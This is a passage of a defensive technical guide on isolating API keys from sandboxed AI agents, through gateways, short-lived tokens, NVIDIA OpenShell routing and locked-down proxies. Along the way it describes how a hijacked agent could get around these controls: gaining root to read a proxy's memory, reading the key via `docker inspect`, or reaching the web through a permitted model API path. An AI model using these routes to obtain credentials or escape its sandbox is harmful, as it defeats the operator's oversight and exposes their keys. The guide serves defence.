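Redirection does help with protocols other than HTTP. netd can insert a username and password into connections that use Redis (a database) or MQTT (a messaging protocol), whereas a model gateway with a base URL receives only requests in the provider's format. An operator who wants to protect only a model key doesn't need this, but if the agent also uses a database and a message queue, it saves building a separate broker for each.

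Both products block a request by default when they can't obtain the credential. LangChain's proxy can fetch a short-lived token from the operator's server, and it rejects the request if the server returns an error or malformed data. In Sandbox0, the agent gets a connection error. Sandbox0 can also be set to let the request continue without a credential, but the provider then returns a 401 error, which makes it look like the key is bad.

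Old keys can also stay in use unnoticed. Sandbox0 says that a new key takes effect immediately for new connections, but also that netd, by default, caches credentials until it restarts. An operator who replaces a leaked key should set a short cache time or restart netd, then confirm that requests use the new key.

### Giving the agent a short-lived credential

With workload identity federation, the agent gets a temporary credential by proving where it is running. Cloud platforms already issue signed statements of identity to the workloads (running programs) they host. The statement is usually a JWT (JSON Web Token), a short text that names the issuer and the workload.

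Anthropic's *Workload Identity Federation* describes how an agent can make requests without a gateway or a stored API key. An administrator tells Anthropic which issuer to trust, creates a service account (an identity for a program rather than a person), and writes a rule that connects the two. When the agent starts, the platform puts a JWT in a file in the sandbox. Anthropic's client library sends the JWT to `/v1/oauth/token`, and Anthropic checks the signature and the rule and returns an access token. The library then puts the access token in the `Authorization` header of the request about the failing test.

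The agent still holds a bearer token. Anyone who steals a copy can use it from anywhere until it expires, unless the operator has restricted which addresses the account accepts requests from. A thief can also copy the JWT and exchange it for more tokens while the JWT is valid.

The token's lifetime depends on the provider. Anthropic allows 60 seconds to 24 hours, with a default of one hour. It also limits the token to twice the time left on the JWT, but never to less than a minute. OpenAI's *Workload identity token exchange* limits the token to one hour or the time left on the JWT, whichever is shorter. By GitGuardian's estimate of how fast attackers act, a one-hour token will often expire before an attacker uses it, but an automated attack can spend a lot in an hour.

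Making a token short-lived doesn't limit what it can do. By default, a token from Anthropic gives the same access as an API key for the same workspace. OpenAI lets administrators restrict a token's permissions but doesn't require it.

The operator has to trust the identity provider and everything it depends on. Anthropic warns that a long-lived cloud credential that can obtain JWTs undermines this arrangement, because anyone who steals it can keep minting new tokens. Ganesan notes that the arrangement suits developers' laptops poorly, since no cloud platform verifies their identity. On a laptop, a developer can approximate it by creating an Anthropic API key that expires in three hours and replacing it by hand.

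Nothing intercepts the traffic, so certificate pinning causes no trouble. However, the agent's software must support the exchange and renew the token. Docker Agent can be configured for the exchange, according to Docker's *Anthropic*.

If an operator forgets to remove an API key when switching to federation, Anthropic's libraries keep using it without any error, because `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` takes precedence over the federation settings. The command `ant auth status` shows which credential is in use. A placeholder key left over from a gateway setup also takes precedence, and requests then fail. According to OpenAI's *Workload identity federation*, OpenAI's coding agent Codex instead chooses federation over any stored key if either of the two required variables is set, and reports incomplete configuration if the other is missing.

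### Signing with a key that cannot be copied

Ganesan's Agent Authenticator, proposed in November 2026, adapts passkeys to agents. A passkey replaces a password with a private key in secure hardware, and the browser makes sure each key works only for its own site. Ganesan replaces the browser with the agent runtime, the trusted program that launches the agent and controls its network connections. A separate program, the authenticator, has access to the hardware keys.

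Before the agent can make a call, the authenticator creates a key pair for that one provider in the machine's secure hardware. A person reads a plain-language description of what the agent may do and signs it with their own passkey. The signed statement, which Ganesan calls a mandate, lists the permitted services and actions, an expiry date, and any actions that need fresh approval. The provider stores the public key and the mandate.

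When the agent tries to ask about the failing test, the provider sends a random challenge. The runtime reads the provider's address from the live TLS connection, so the model can't choose it. The authenticator checks the mandate, then signs the address, the challenge, a counter and the requested action. If the signature and mandate are valid, the provider issues a short-lived token tied to the agent's key through DPoP, a standard that requires the client to prove with each request that it has the private key. The agent can then send its question.

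A copied token is useless elsewhere without the private key, which the hardware does not release. But someone who controls the agent can still request whatever the mandate permits, so this design also has the confused-deputy problem. The operator must trust the hardware maker, the runtime and the authenticator, and the person who signs the mandate has to read it.

The authenticator signs only for processes it launched and their descendants. It enforces this with a software check, which Ganesan acknowledges an administrator can defeat. The check also offers little protection against a malicious package that the agent installs, because the installation script descends from the agent. Ganesan lists the Nx attack as blocked because there would have been no credentials on disk and no readable keys. The attackers could not have stolen a key, but a script started by the agent could still have requested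 signatures within the mandate.

Ganesan has not built a full implementation and reports no measurements. His verdicts on past incidents are his own reading of the incident reports. The design requires providers to verify the signatures and proofs, so an operator can't adopt it alone. Registration would fail with a provider that doesn't support the design, and only Ganesan's fallback broker would work.

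OpenAI offers part of this today. OpenAI's *Configure workload identity federation with X.509 certificates* describes how a program proves its identity with a client certificate and receives a token that lasts at most an hour. The program must then present both the token and an accepted certificate with each API request. The certificate's private key can be kept in hardware, since OpenAI's Java library accepts hardware-backed keys. But the token isn't tied to one certificate, so a thief who has any other certificate that the project accepts can use it with a stolen token. Codex doesn't support this method.

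### Whether a key behind a proxy is good enough

Ganesan objects that a proxied key is still a bearer token. This objection applies to the gateway itself, because anyone who breaks into it can copy the key and use it anywhere.

The usual reply is that providers accept nothing better. Posta argues this in *Credential Injection Patterns for AI Agents*, in response to an internet draft by Kenneth Hartman. The draft recommends giving agents short-lived tokens tied to a key and using a proxy only as a fallback, while Posta would use the proxy first. A tied token is safe only if the issuer ties it to the key and the receiving service checks this on every request, and he points out that GitHub tokens, API keys and most business software don't support this. He works on a commercial gateway of the kind he recommends, but OpenAI's documentation supports him on this point, since its tokens don't use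 DPoP, a standard for tying tokens to keys.

The large providers now offer alternatives to long-lived API keys. Anthropic and OpenAI accept workload identity, as does OpenRouter, a service that resells access to many models, on its Business and Enterprise plans, according to OpenRouter's *Workload identity federation*. The Gemini API accepts OAuth tokens, as Google's *Authentication with OAuth quickstart* explains, and Google Cloud's service-account tokens last one hour by default. Google has also replaced its standard Gemini keys with "auth keys". Google's *Using Gemini API keys* explains that each belongs to a service account, which allows finer permissions, but they are still API keys that a thief can copy.

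Amazon's cloud services normally use SigV4, in which the client signs each request with a secret key but never sends the key. A proxy can't just replace a placeholder key in such a request, because the signature was made with the placeholder. It has to sign the request again with the real key. Amazon later also added bearer keys for Bedrock, its model service. Wiz's *A new type of long-lived key on AWS* reports finding leaked Bedrock keys on GitHub within two weeks of the launch. AWS's *API keys* recommends long-term keys only for exploration and short-term keys, which last up to 12 hours, for production.

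| Provider | Alternative to a long-lived API key | How long it lasts | Whether a stolen copy works elsewhere |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Token issued for a workload identity | 1 hour by default, 24 hours at most | Yes, until it expires |
| OpenAI | Token issued for a workload identity or client certificate | 1 hour at most | Yes, unless the project requires a client certificate |
| Google, Gemini API | OAuth token | 1 hour by default for a service account | Yes, until it expires |
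| Amazon Bedrock | Short-term key | 12 hours at most | Yes, until it expires |
| Amazon Bedrock | SigV4 signature on each request | Secret stays with the client | The request doesn't contain the secret |

Ganesan describes most of these credentials correctly, but an operator can reduce the risk without waiting for his design. The gateway can obtain the short-lived token and add it to requests, so the agent has no credential and the gateway has no long-lived provider key. Posta's open-source agentgateway can perform such token exchanges. The operator still needs to protect whatever the gateway uses to prove its identity.

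An operator who uses OpenAI's API can also make a stolen key useless on its own. OpenAI's *Mutual TLS* describes a setting that makes a project reject requests without an accepted client certificate, even if the key is valid. The gateway can hold the certificate, so the agent doesn't have to handle it. The operator should test the setting by sending a request with a valid key but no certificate, which should return the error `certificate_required`.

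### Matching the design to the situation

For an agent that reads untrusted text or installs packages, a gateway is safer than even a short-lived token because the agent holds no credential that works outside the sandbox. The simplest gateway design for a builder who only needs model calls is to change the base URL. TLS interception is worth the extra work when the software can't change its base URL or when the same proxy has to handle many other services.

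| Situation | Design | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's software has a base URL setting and needs only model calls | Gateway address with a dummy key | Only the intended sandbox can reach the gateway |
| Many sandboxes share a gateway | Gateway address with a token for each sandbox | A token copied to another sandbox fails |
| A developer runs several coding agents on a laptop and they also use GitHub | Placeholder swapped by a proxy on the host, as in Docker Sandboxes | OAuth logins leave no real token in the sandbox |
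| The agent runs programs that ignore proxy settings, or uses databases and message queues | Redirection in the network | Requests fail when the credential is missing, and a replaced key takes effect |
| The software pins certificates and has a fixed address | Short-lived credential if the software supports it, otherwise a capped key that expires soon | The provider enforces the spending limit |
| A cloud job runs only trusted code on trusted input | Short-lived credential held by the job | No old API key overrides it |
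| A cloud job reads text from strangers | Gateway that obtains the short-lived credential itself | The agent can't read the gateway's identity token |
| A high-limit OpenAI account needs protection against theft from the gateway | Gateway with a client certificate as well as a key or token | The key fails without the certificate |
| Policy requires a separate hardware-held key for each agent and provider | Agent Authenticator, once someone has built it and the provider accepts it | Until then, use a gateway |

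## Setting up the local inference endpoint

OpenShell is NVIDIA's sandbox runtime for AI agents. Agents reach a model API at `https://inference.local`, an address that works only inside the sandbox. OpenShell removes any credential the agent sends there and adds the real one. NVIDIA's *Inference Routing* describes the route in enough detail to copy it or compare another gateway with it.

Anyone installing OpenShell should check the release first, because newer ones work differently. skills.sh's *Debug Inference* (2026), a copy of NVIDIA's troubleshooting instructions, states that OpenShell "no longer supplies a managed inference route". In NVIDIA's OpenShell v0.1.2 walk-through, *Isolate AI coding agents like Pi with kernel-level policies*, the agent calls the provider's address directly. NemoClaw, NVIDIA's ready-made stack for running agents such as OpenClaw and Hermes on OpenShell, still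 uses the endpoint. According to NVIDIA's *Architecture Details*, NemoClaw's managed installations require OpenShell 0.0.116 and send some model traffic through `inference.local`. The procedure below applies if `openshell inference --help` lists the subcommands `set` and `get`.

In OpenShell, two programs share the work of an inference gateway. The first, which NVIDIA calls the gateway, stores the provider keys and configuration and creates the sandboxes. The second, the supervisor, runs in each sandbox, starts the agent with reduced privileges and filters its traffic. "OpenShell gateway" here means the program that stores the keys.

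### From the agent to the router

In the earlier example, a coding agent asks Claude to explain a failing test. The agent, Claude Code, runs in an OpenShell sandbox with `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` set to `https://inference.local`. It sends the test output in the body of a `POST /v1/messages` request.

The agent runs in its own network namespace, a Linux feature that gives a process a separate view of the network. From there it can reach only OpenShell's proxy, at `10.200.0.1`. Claude Code asks the proxy for a tunnel to `inference.local` by sending an HTTP CONNECT request. The proxy handles connections to that name itself, before it checks the egress rules. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* explains that a process that ignores its proxy settings still can't reach anything else. The agent therefore doesn't need direct access to the provider,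 and the operator can block it completely.

HTTP clients often reuse an open connection. An agent could try to exploit this by making a model request and then sending a request for a different host over the same connection. The proxy refuses the second request and closes the connection.

The proxy has to terminate TLS to read the model request. OpenShell generates a certificate authority for each sandbox at startup and makes the programs inside trust it by setting environment variables such as `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS`, `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` and `CURL_CA_BUNDLE`. NVIDIA's list covers Node.js, Deno, Python's Requests library, curl and Git. It has no variable for Java, so the builder will probably have to add the authority to Java's trust store. If someone steals one sandbox's signing key, the harm is limited because programs in other sandboxes don't trust that sandbox's authority.

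### What the router lets through

After decryption, the request goes to the inference router, which NVIDIA also calls the privacy router. The router checks the request's method and path against a short list for the provider and denies any request that doesn't match.

| Provider | Permitted requests | Caller's headers that pass |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI and compatible services | `POST` to `/v1/chat/completions`, `/v1/completions`, `/v1/responses` and `/v1/embeddings`; `GET` on `/v1/models` and `/v1/models/*` | `openai-organization`, `x-model-id` |
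| Anthropic | `POST` to `/v1/messages` | `anthropic-version`, `anthropic-beta` |
| Claude through Google Vertex AI | `POST` to `/v1/messages` | Neither of Anthropic's headers; the router writes the version into the body |

An API key often permits much more than model calls. An OpenAI key with full permissions can list and download the account's stored files or start a fine-tuning job. Path matching stops the agent from using the operator's key for such requests. The path can also determine whether a reply contains a secret, as "Keeping the key out of what the agent gets back" explains.

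The router's path list doesn't restrict the contents of the request body. An agent can still use a permitted `POST /v1/responses` to have OpenAI search the web from its own servers, so an agent in a sandbox with no internet access may get some access through the model API. To prevent this, an operator must also filter the tools that a request names.

Next, the router removes the caller's `Authorization` and `x-api-key` headers, along with any others that aren't on its list of allowed headers. As with Docker's proxy, this prevents an attacker from having the agent send files to the provider under the attacker's own key.

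A list of permitted headers is safer than a list of forbidden ones because the router drops any new header until someone allows it. A forbidden list works only if the builder knows every header that can carry a credential or change who pays, and updates the list whenever the provider adds one. The drawback of a permitted list is that the router also drops harmless headers without notifying the client. If a client turns on a feature or labels a request through an unlisted header, the request may still succeed without the feature or label.

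Some permitted headers let an agent make choices that a builder may want to prevent. OpenAI uses `openai-organization` to decide which organisation to bill when a key works for more than one, so an agent could choose which one is billed. A key that belongs to a single project avoids this. An agent can also use `anthropic-beta` to turn on features that Anthropic is still testing, and a builder who doesn't need them can leave that header off the permitted list.

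The router then replaces the model name in the request body with the one the operator has configured. NVIDIA's Python examples set the model name to `anything`, and the request still works. Replacing the name stops the agent, or someone who has hijacked it, from choosing the provider's most expensive model or one the operator hasn't approved. It doesn't limit the number or length of the agent's requests.

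Rewriting can also raise the bill, because coding agents often send small background jobs, such as naming a session, to a cheaper model, and the router sends those to the configured model too. A request written for one model may contain options that another rejects. The agent's logs may show the model it requested rather than the one used, so anyone comparing models should take the name from the operator's configuration.

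### Adding the key and returning the answer

The router takes the provider key from the provider record, which is the operator's stored entry for one model service, and adds it to the request. It forwards the request to the address in the same record, so the agent can't choose the host. For Vertex AI, the record can supply a short-lived Google token instead of a permanent key.

The provider streams the answer in small pieces, and the router passes them on as they arrive. If the router waited for the whole answer, a client might time out before receiving anything. Some models spend a long time reasoning before they write, so the router allows gaps of up to 120 seconds between pieces.

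A separate timeout, 60 seconds by default, applies to the whole request. NVIDIA advises raising it for models with long thinking phases. With the default, a request times out before a 120-second gap in output can occur. With a 300-second timeout, a request can still fail if the model sends no output for more than 120 seconds.

### Which process holds the key

NVIDIA's documents conflict about where routing and authentication happen. Its security guide calls the router "sandbox-local" but also says that the OpenShell gateway "injects credentials on the host side". NVIDIA's June 2026 summary, *Which sandbox runtime handles model authentication at the gateway*, places authentication at the gateway but the router inside the sandbox. The NemoClaw architecture page lists the proxy that adds credentials as a gateway process, which normally runs on the host.

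NVIDIA's *How OpenShell Works*, the most specific account, describes a supervisor that runs "inside every sandbox workload", meaning the container, pod or virtual machine that also contains the agent. The supervisor receives credentials from the OpenShell gateway and adds them to requests. The diagram also places the inference router in the sandbox and shows it connected directly to the model's servers, bypassing the gateway.

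This account is the one to plan around because it describes OpenShell itself and follows the credential from one process to the next, whereas the NemoClaw page describes a product built on OpenShell. The OpenShell gateway stores the key, and the supervisor's side of the sandbox has it in memory while using it. "Host side" probably refers to a position in the network. OpenShell connects the agent's namespace to the proxy with a pair of virtual network interfaces, and NVIDIA calls the proxy's end the host side. That end is outside the agent's namespace but can still be inside the container.

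On a Linux host that runs the sandbox in Docker, an operator can check whether the inference router is inside the container by running `sudo tcpdump -ni any port 443` while the agent waits for a long answer. The command shows which addresses are exchanging encrypted traffic. If the container's own address is exchanging traffic with the provider, the router and the API key are both inside the container.

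The location matters when an attacker gets further than the agent's own process:

| What the attacker controls | Key in the supervisor | Key only in a process on the host |
|---|---|---|
| The agent and its subprocesses | Can make model calls but can't read the key | The same |
| Root in the container or virtual machine | Can probably read the key from the supervisor's memory | Can make model calls, but needs a further break-in to read the key |
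| The host | Can read the key | Can read the key |

OpenShell puts several barriers between the agent and the supervisor. The agent runs as a non-root user, and a system-call filter blocks `ptrace` and `process_vm_readv`, which can read another process's memory. Landlock, a Linux kernel feature, limits which files the agent can open. By default, OpenShell starts the sandbox even if the kernel doesn't support Landlock, and only logs a high-severity warning. Setting `compatibility: hard_requirement` prevents the sandbox from starting without Landlock support.

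A virtual machine protects the host better than a container does, but it adds little protection for the key. A kernel flaw that gives an attacker root in a container often gives them the host as well, and then it hardly matters which process had the key. An attacker who gains root in a virtual machine is still cut off from the host, but can probably read the key because the supervisor is in the same virtual machine.

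Storing the key in the supervisor also means that ten sandboxes using the same provider need ten copies of the key, one in each supervisor. A breach of any one supervisor forces the operator to replace the key for all ten.

Still, this arrangement can expose fewer credentials than a proxy on the host if the proxy is compromised. The proxy has to parse requests that an attacker can craft, and its parser may have bugs. An attacker who exploits one to take over a supervisor gets the credentials that supervisor's sandbox uses. If the same code ran in the OpenShell gateway, the attacker might get every credential stored there.

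An operator who wants to keep the key out of the workload entirely can run a second gateway on another machine. The provider record then contains that gateway's address and token instead of the provider's address and key, so someone who breaks into the supervisor gets only the token.

### Creating the route

The operator runs these commands outside the sandbox, in a shell where `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` contains the real key:

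```shell
openshell provider create --name anthropic-prod --type anthropic --from-existing
openshell inference set --provider anthropic-prod --model <model-id> --timeout 300
openshell inference get
```

`--from-existing` copies the key from the environment into a provider record. The alternative, `--credential`, takes the key on the command line, where the shell may save it in its history. After creating the record, the operator should delete the key from the shell profile and any `.env` file. The section "Storing the key and protecting the gateway" covers the copy that remains in the provider record.

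`inference set` sets the provider and model for the endpoint. It contacts the upstream before saving, so it usually detects a wrong address. `--no-verify` skips this check if the model server isn't running yet. `inference get` prints the provider, model and timeout.

The operator then opens a sandbox with `openshell sandbox create`. According to NVIDIA, the shortcut `openshell sandbox create -- claude` can also find the developer's Anthropic key, create a provider and attach it to the sandbox, which gives the agent a placeholder for the provider's own address. An operator who wants the agent to use only `inference.local` should open a plain sandbox and start Claude Code by hand.

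A request with no key tests the whole route from inside the sandbox:

```shell
curl https://inference.local/v1/messages \
  -H "content-type: application/json" \
  -H "anthropic-version: 2023-06-01" \
  -d '{"model": "anything", "max_tokens": 20,
       "messages": [{"role": "user", "content": "Hello"}]}'
```

A JSON reply from the model confirms that the router accepted the path, replaced the model name and added a working key. NVIDIA's example posts to `/v1/responses`, which suits an OpenAI-compatible provider. With an Anthropic provider, the router denies that path even when the setup is correct.

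Claude Code can then start with a dummy key:

```shell
ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL="https://inference.local" ANTHROPIC_API_KEY=unused claude --bare
```

The `--bare` option skips the browser login, which could otherwise leave a real token in the sandbox.

### When requests fail

The `curl` test shows whether a fault is in the route or in the agent's settings. If `curl` works but the agent doesn't, the cause is usually the base URL or the login.

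| Sign | Likely cause | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| `curl` works, but the router denies Claude Code's first message | The base URL ends in `/v1`, so Claude Code asks for `/v1/v1/messages` | Remove `/v1` from the base URL |
| `curl` works, but the router denies OpenCode's first message | The base URL lacks `/v1`, so OpenCode asks for `/messages` | Add `/v1` |
| Claude Code asks the user to log in | It is trying OAuth before the API key | Start it with `--bare` |
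| A local model answers on the host but not through the router | The upstream address is `localhost`, or the model server listens only on `127.0.0.1` | Use `host.openshell.internal` and make the server listen on an address the router can reach |
| Short answers arrive, but long ones fail after about a minute | The 60-second default timeout | `openshell inference update --timeout 300` |
| Messages work, but one feature of the client fails | The feature uses a path outside the permitted list | Turn the feature off or choose a client that doesn't need it |
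| A script can't reach the endpoint at all | The script calls `http://inference.local` | Use `https://` |

The `/v1` fault is common because clients handle that part of the address differently. OpenAI's Python library expects it in the base URL, while Anthropic's adds it. The error code isn't a reliable guide. *Troubleshooting Aperture*, from the networking company Tailscale, says that a doubled `/v1` in Aperture, a comparable gateway, produces HTTP error 405, which looks more like a wrong method than a wrong path. Writing out the full address that the client will request and comparing it with the permitted list is quicker.

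Denied paths can be confusing because most of the agent still works. Anthropic's API has separate paths for counting the tokens in a message (`/v1/messages/count_tokens`) and for listing models. Neither is on OpenShell's list of allowed paths for Anthropic, so OpenShell denies a client's calls to them while letting its ordinary messages through.

The `localhost` fault occurs because the name refers to the machine or namespace that makes the request. An address that works in the operator's terminal, where `localhost` is the host, therefore fails from the router, where it refers to somewhere else. NVIDIA's *Run Local Inference with Ollama* uses `http://host.openshell.internal:11434/v1` for Ollama, a program that runs models locally, and starts Ollama on `0.0.0.0`, which means every network interface. Ubuntu's *Use inference snaps in OpenShell* also sets its model server to listen on `0.0.0.0`,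 but puts the machine's hostname in the provider record.

If the model server listens on every interface, other computers on the network may be able to use the model without a key, so the operator should add a firewall rule that admits only the sandboxes and the gateway. If the OpenShell gateway runs on a remote server, `host.openshell.internal` refers to that server, so a model on the developer's laptop needs a tunnel.

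### Closing the direct route to the provider

The router doesn't check requests sent directly to `api.anthropic.com`. OpenShell treats them as ordinary outbound traffic, subject to the sandbox's egress rules (`network_policies`). These rules deny every destination by default, and NVIDIA advises operators against allowing model providers' hosts. If those hosts were allowed, an old key left in the project or one supplied by an attacker would work from inside the sandbox.

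An operator could easily open the direct route to `api.anthropic.com` by accident. When an agent tries an address outside the policy, OpenShell blocks the request and asks the operator whether to allow it. If Claude Code starts without `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, it calls `api.anthropic.com`, and the operator may approve the familiar address. The request then fails because it has no valid key, and the operator corrects the base URL. Claude Code now works, but the direct route stays open until someone removes it from the policy or recreates the sandbox.

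To check that the sandbox can't reach Anthropic directly, the operator can run `curl -i https://api.anthropic.com/v1/messages` inside it. OpenShell should refuse the connection. An error from Anthropic, such as a 401 for a missing key, means the request got through.

If an agent needs another service on a provider's host, the operator has to open a route to it. OpenShell can limit that route to particular methods and paths, but by default the proxy only logs violations and still forwards the requests. To block them, the operator has to set `enforcement: enforce`.

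### One provider and one model for every sandbox

Each OpenShell gateway has a single provider and a single model behind `inference.local`, and every sandbox on that gateway uses them. A change reaches running sandboxes within about five seconds, so an operator can replace a leaked key without restarting any agents.

One person's change also affects everyone else on the gateway. A developer who wants to try a cheaper model and runs `openshell inference update --model` switches every other agent to it, possibly halfway through a task. Changing from Anthropic to an OpenAI-compatible provider also changes the permitted paths. Claude Code's next request would still go to `/v1/messages`, and the router would deny it because the route now accepts only OpenAI's paths. For the same reason, a team can't run Claude Code against Anthropic and an OpenAI-format agent against OpenAI through `inference.local`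 on one gateway.

Changing the provider can have more serious consequences for confidential work. If a company has approved one provider for a customer's code and a colleague switches the gateway to another, the agent's next request will send any customer code in the conversation to a provider the customer never agreed to.

The provider also sees one key for all the sandboxes, so its bill doesn't show which agent spent the money, and one runaway agent can use up the rate limit for the rest. The operator needs separate records for each sandbox to identify the agent responsible, and also needs the limits described in "Limiting what an agent can do through the gateway".

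Sandboxes that need different providers, budgets or levels of confidentiality should use separate OpenShell gateways, each with its own key. On a shared gateway, only the person responsible for it should be able to run `openshell inference set`.

### Attached providers in newer releases

NVIDIA's newer design avoids the shared setting by attaching a provider to each sandbox, so changing one sandbox's provider doesn't affect the others. The agent calls the provider's normal address with a placeholder key, and OpenShell replaces it with the real key as the request goes out. NVIDIA's *About Inference Routing* explains that NemoClaw now uses this design for new sandboxes that use OpenAI, Anthropic, Google Gemini and several other hosted services. Older sandboxes without an attached provider, and some that use local or custom model servers, keep the shared `inference.local` route.

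If a sandbox's recorded provider is missing or doesn't match, NemoClaw stops instead of falling back to the shared route. This is safer than Docker's fallback to a global secret.

In OpenShell v0.1.2, the operator writes a provider profile that lists the permitted hosts and the programs that may call them, then starts the sandbox with `--provider <name>`. The agent's settings must contain the provider's real address and a valid model name, because OpenShell no longer rewrites the model name. An operator who relied on rewriting to keep agents off expensive models needs another way to restrict them.

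The list of permitted programs gives less protection than it seems to. NVIDIA's example profile permits Node.js because the agent runs on it, and Python and curl because the agent's tools use them. A malicious npm package also runs on Node.js, so it can reach the model API as easily as the agent can.

If a program isn't on the list of allowed programs, the agent reports only a connection error. The troubleshooting table in NVIDIA's *Isolate AI coding agents like Pi with kernel-level policies* explains that `openshell logs <sandbox-name> --tail` shows `DENIED` when the policy blocked the request, and `NET:FAIL` when the policy allowed it but the model server didn't respond. After changing a credential, the operator has to restart the agent, because a running process keeps the placeholder it started with.

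The advice to keep the provider's host out of the egress rules no longer applies either. According to NVIDIA's *Providers v2*, attaching a provider adds entries for it to the sandbox's network policy, so the sandbox can reach the provider directly by design. Protection then depends on how the proxy handles a request that contains a different key instead of the placeholder. If it forwards that key unchanged, uploads to an attacker's account become possible again. Before relying on this design, a builder should send a request from the sandbox with a valid key from a second account and check that OpenShell blocks the request or replaces the key.

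## Storing the key and protecting the gateway

The command `openshell provider create` stores the real key in a provider record on the host. Anyone who can read the OpenShell gateway's files, backups or memory can copy the key, and the same is true of other gateways. The operator has to choose storage that the agent can't read, delete copies of the key made before the gateway was set up, and defend the gateway, which is now a better target for attackers than any single sandbox.

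### Choosing where to store the key

| Storage | Who can read the key | Other copies it tends to create |
|---|---|---|
| File that only the gateway's account can open | The gateway's account and the host's administrator | Backups and disk snapshots |
| Operating-system keychain | Often any program under the same account while the keychain is unlocked | Exports and synchronised copies |
| Environment variable | The gateway, its child processes, other processes under the same account, and the host's administrator | The file or command that set the variable |
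| External secrets manager | Its administrators and anyone who can log in to it as the gateway | The login credential on the gateway's host |

A running gateway has the key in memory wherever it came from, so the host's administrator can read it in all four cases.

For one gateway on one Linux server, a file is usually enough. The operator creates an account for the gateway and a file that only this account can open:

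```shell
sudo useradd --system --shell /usr/sbin/nologin model-gateway
sudo install -d -m 700 -o model-gateway /etc/model-gateway
sudo install -m 600 -o model-gateway /dev/null /etc/model-gateway/provider-key
sudo -u model-gateway sh -c 'cat > /etc/model-gateway/provider-key'
```

The last command waits for the operator to paste the key, press Enter and then press Ctrl-D. The key never appears in a command, so it isn't saved in the shell history. If the gateway later gives a malformed-header error, the line break at the end of the file is a likely cause.

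A keychain, such as Keychain on macOS or GNOME Keyring on Linux, encrypts secrets and unlocks them when the user logs in. It protects the key if someone steals a laptop that is switched off, but much less so against malicious code running under the developer's account. GNOME Keyring normally releases an unlocked secret to any program in the user's session, while macOS can prompt the user before a new program reads one. Docker Sandboxes can rely on the keychain because the agent runs in a sandbox, outside the developer's session. On a server, nobody logs in to unlock a keychain.

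An environment variable is the easiest option to set up and the least secure. Crash reports sometimes include environment variables, and the key is usually on disk as well, because the variable has to be set from a service definition, a script or a container configuration.

The gateway can fetch the key at startup from a secrets manager such as HashiCorp Vault or AWS Secrets Manager, which is the kind of vault Fly.io used. A secrets manager can record each request for a secret, and it is easier to control than a set of files when there are several gateways or administrators. But the gateway needs a credential to log in, and on an ordinary server that credential is often stored in a file with the same permissions the key would have had.

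A startup script that fetches the key and exports it to the agent undoes the benefit, as OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns.

### Running the gateway under its own account

File permissions restrict access by account, so if the gateway and the agent both run as `alice`, both can open the key file even if its mode is 600. The gateway therefore needs its own account, and the agent's account must have no way to gain administrator rights.

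Codex uses this arrangement in GitHub Actions, where all the steps of a job normally share one virtual machine. The workflow gives the OpenAI key to OpenAI's *Codex GitHub Action*, which starts a small proxy and points Codex at it. OpenAI's *codex-responses-api-proxy*, the proxy's documentation in the Codex repository, explains how it handles the key:

1. A privileged user pipes the key into the proxy's standard input. The same command removes `OPENAI_API_KEY` from the proxy's environment, so the key doesn't appear there in `/proc`.
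2. The proxy builds the text of the `Authorization` header in a temporary buffer, copies it to the memory it will use for requests, and overwrites the buffer with zeros.
3. It asks the operating system to lock that memory so that the key isn't written to the swap file on disk.
4. Codex runs under an unprivileged account and sends its requests to a port on `127.0.0.1`. The proxy accepts only `POST /v1/responses`, replaces the `Authorization` header and forwards the request to OpenAI. It answers anything else with a 403 error.

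The proxy also uses a small library that runs before the main program. According to OpenAI's *codex-process-hardening*, the library disables core dumps (copies of a program's memory saved after a crash), stops debuggers from attaching on Linux and macOS, and removes environment variables such as `LD_PRELOAD` that can load extra code into a program.

These measures stop ordinary users but not an administrator. On Linux, root can read another process's memory through `/proc/<pid>/mem`, even when the process has refused debuggers and locked its memory. The default account on a GitHub runner typically has `sudo`, so a hijacked Codex could become root and search the proxy's memory for the key. The action has four settings to deal with this:

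| Setting | What it does | Whether the key is protected from Codex |
|---|---|---|
| `drop-sudo` (default) | Removes the account's `sudo` rights for the rest of the job | Yes, unless the account has another way to become root |
| `unprivileged-user` | Runs Codex under a separate account that the operator names | Yes, on the same condition |
| `read-only` | Stops Codex from changing files or using the network directly, but leaves its privileges | No |
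| `unsafe` | Restricts nothing | No |

`read-only` is not the safest option, because copying a key from memory only requires reading. The agent could then include the key in its final message, which many workflows post as a public comment. OpenAI's online guide, *Codex GitHub Action*, says not to rely on this setting alone to protect secrets. Windows runners support only `unsafe`, so a job that reads strangers' pull requests should run on Linux or macOS.

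Removing `sudo` doesn't help if the agent's account can still use Docker, so the operator should check that the account isn't in the `docker` group. Later steps in the job also lose `sudo`, and OpenAI advises making Codex the last step.

Some agents need administrator rights, for example to install system packages. They should have those rights only inside their own virtual machine, and the gateway should run on a different machine. An agent that becomes root can then read everything on its own machine without finding the key.

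### Running the gateway in its own container

GitHub faced the same problem with Agentic Workflows, its product for running agents in GitHub Actions. It moved the model keys to a sidecar, a helper container that runs beside the agent's container (GitHub, *Under the hood*, 2026).

Two documents in GitHub's `gh-aw-firewall` repository, *API Proxy Sidecar* and *Authentication Architecture*, describe how a sidecar keeps API keys away from the agent. The command-line tool reads the keys on the host and passes them only to the sidecar. The agent's `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` is `http://172.30.0.30:10001`, the sidecar's address on a private network. The sidecar removes any authentication headers the agent sent, adds the real key and sends the request through Squid, a proxy that allows only listed domains. Before the agent starts, a script checks that the agent's environment contains no API keys and that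 the sidecar responds. If either check fails, the agent doesn't run.

The sidecar has memory and process limits and runs without Linux capabilities, the separate permissions that make up root's power. It rejects request bodies over 10 MB, which could affect agents that send many images.

The key is still in two places on the host, the sidecar's environment and the Docker Compose file. Anyone who can read that file can get the key, and so can anyone who can use Docker, since `docker inspect awf-api-proxy` prints the container's environment. The firewall's `--enable-dind` option gives an agent this Docker access by exposing the host's Docker socket. GitHub deletes a hosted runner's virtual machine after each job, but on a self-hosted runner or a laptop the file can remain after the job ends.

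A container boundary also depends on everything that can control the containers. GitHub's *Security Architecture* lists the kernel, the container runtime and three privileged containers among the trusted parts. One of these containers, the MCP gateway, starts tool servers through the Docker socket. It handles the agent's tool calls and no model requests, but an attacker who took it over could read the model keys.

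| | GitHub's sidecar | OpenAI's Codex proxy |
|---|---|---|
| What separates it from the agent | A container | A user account |
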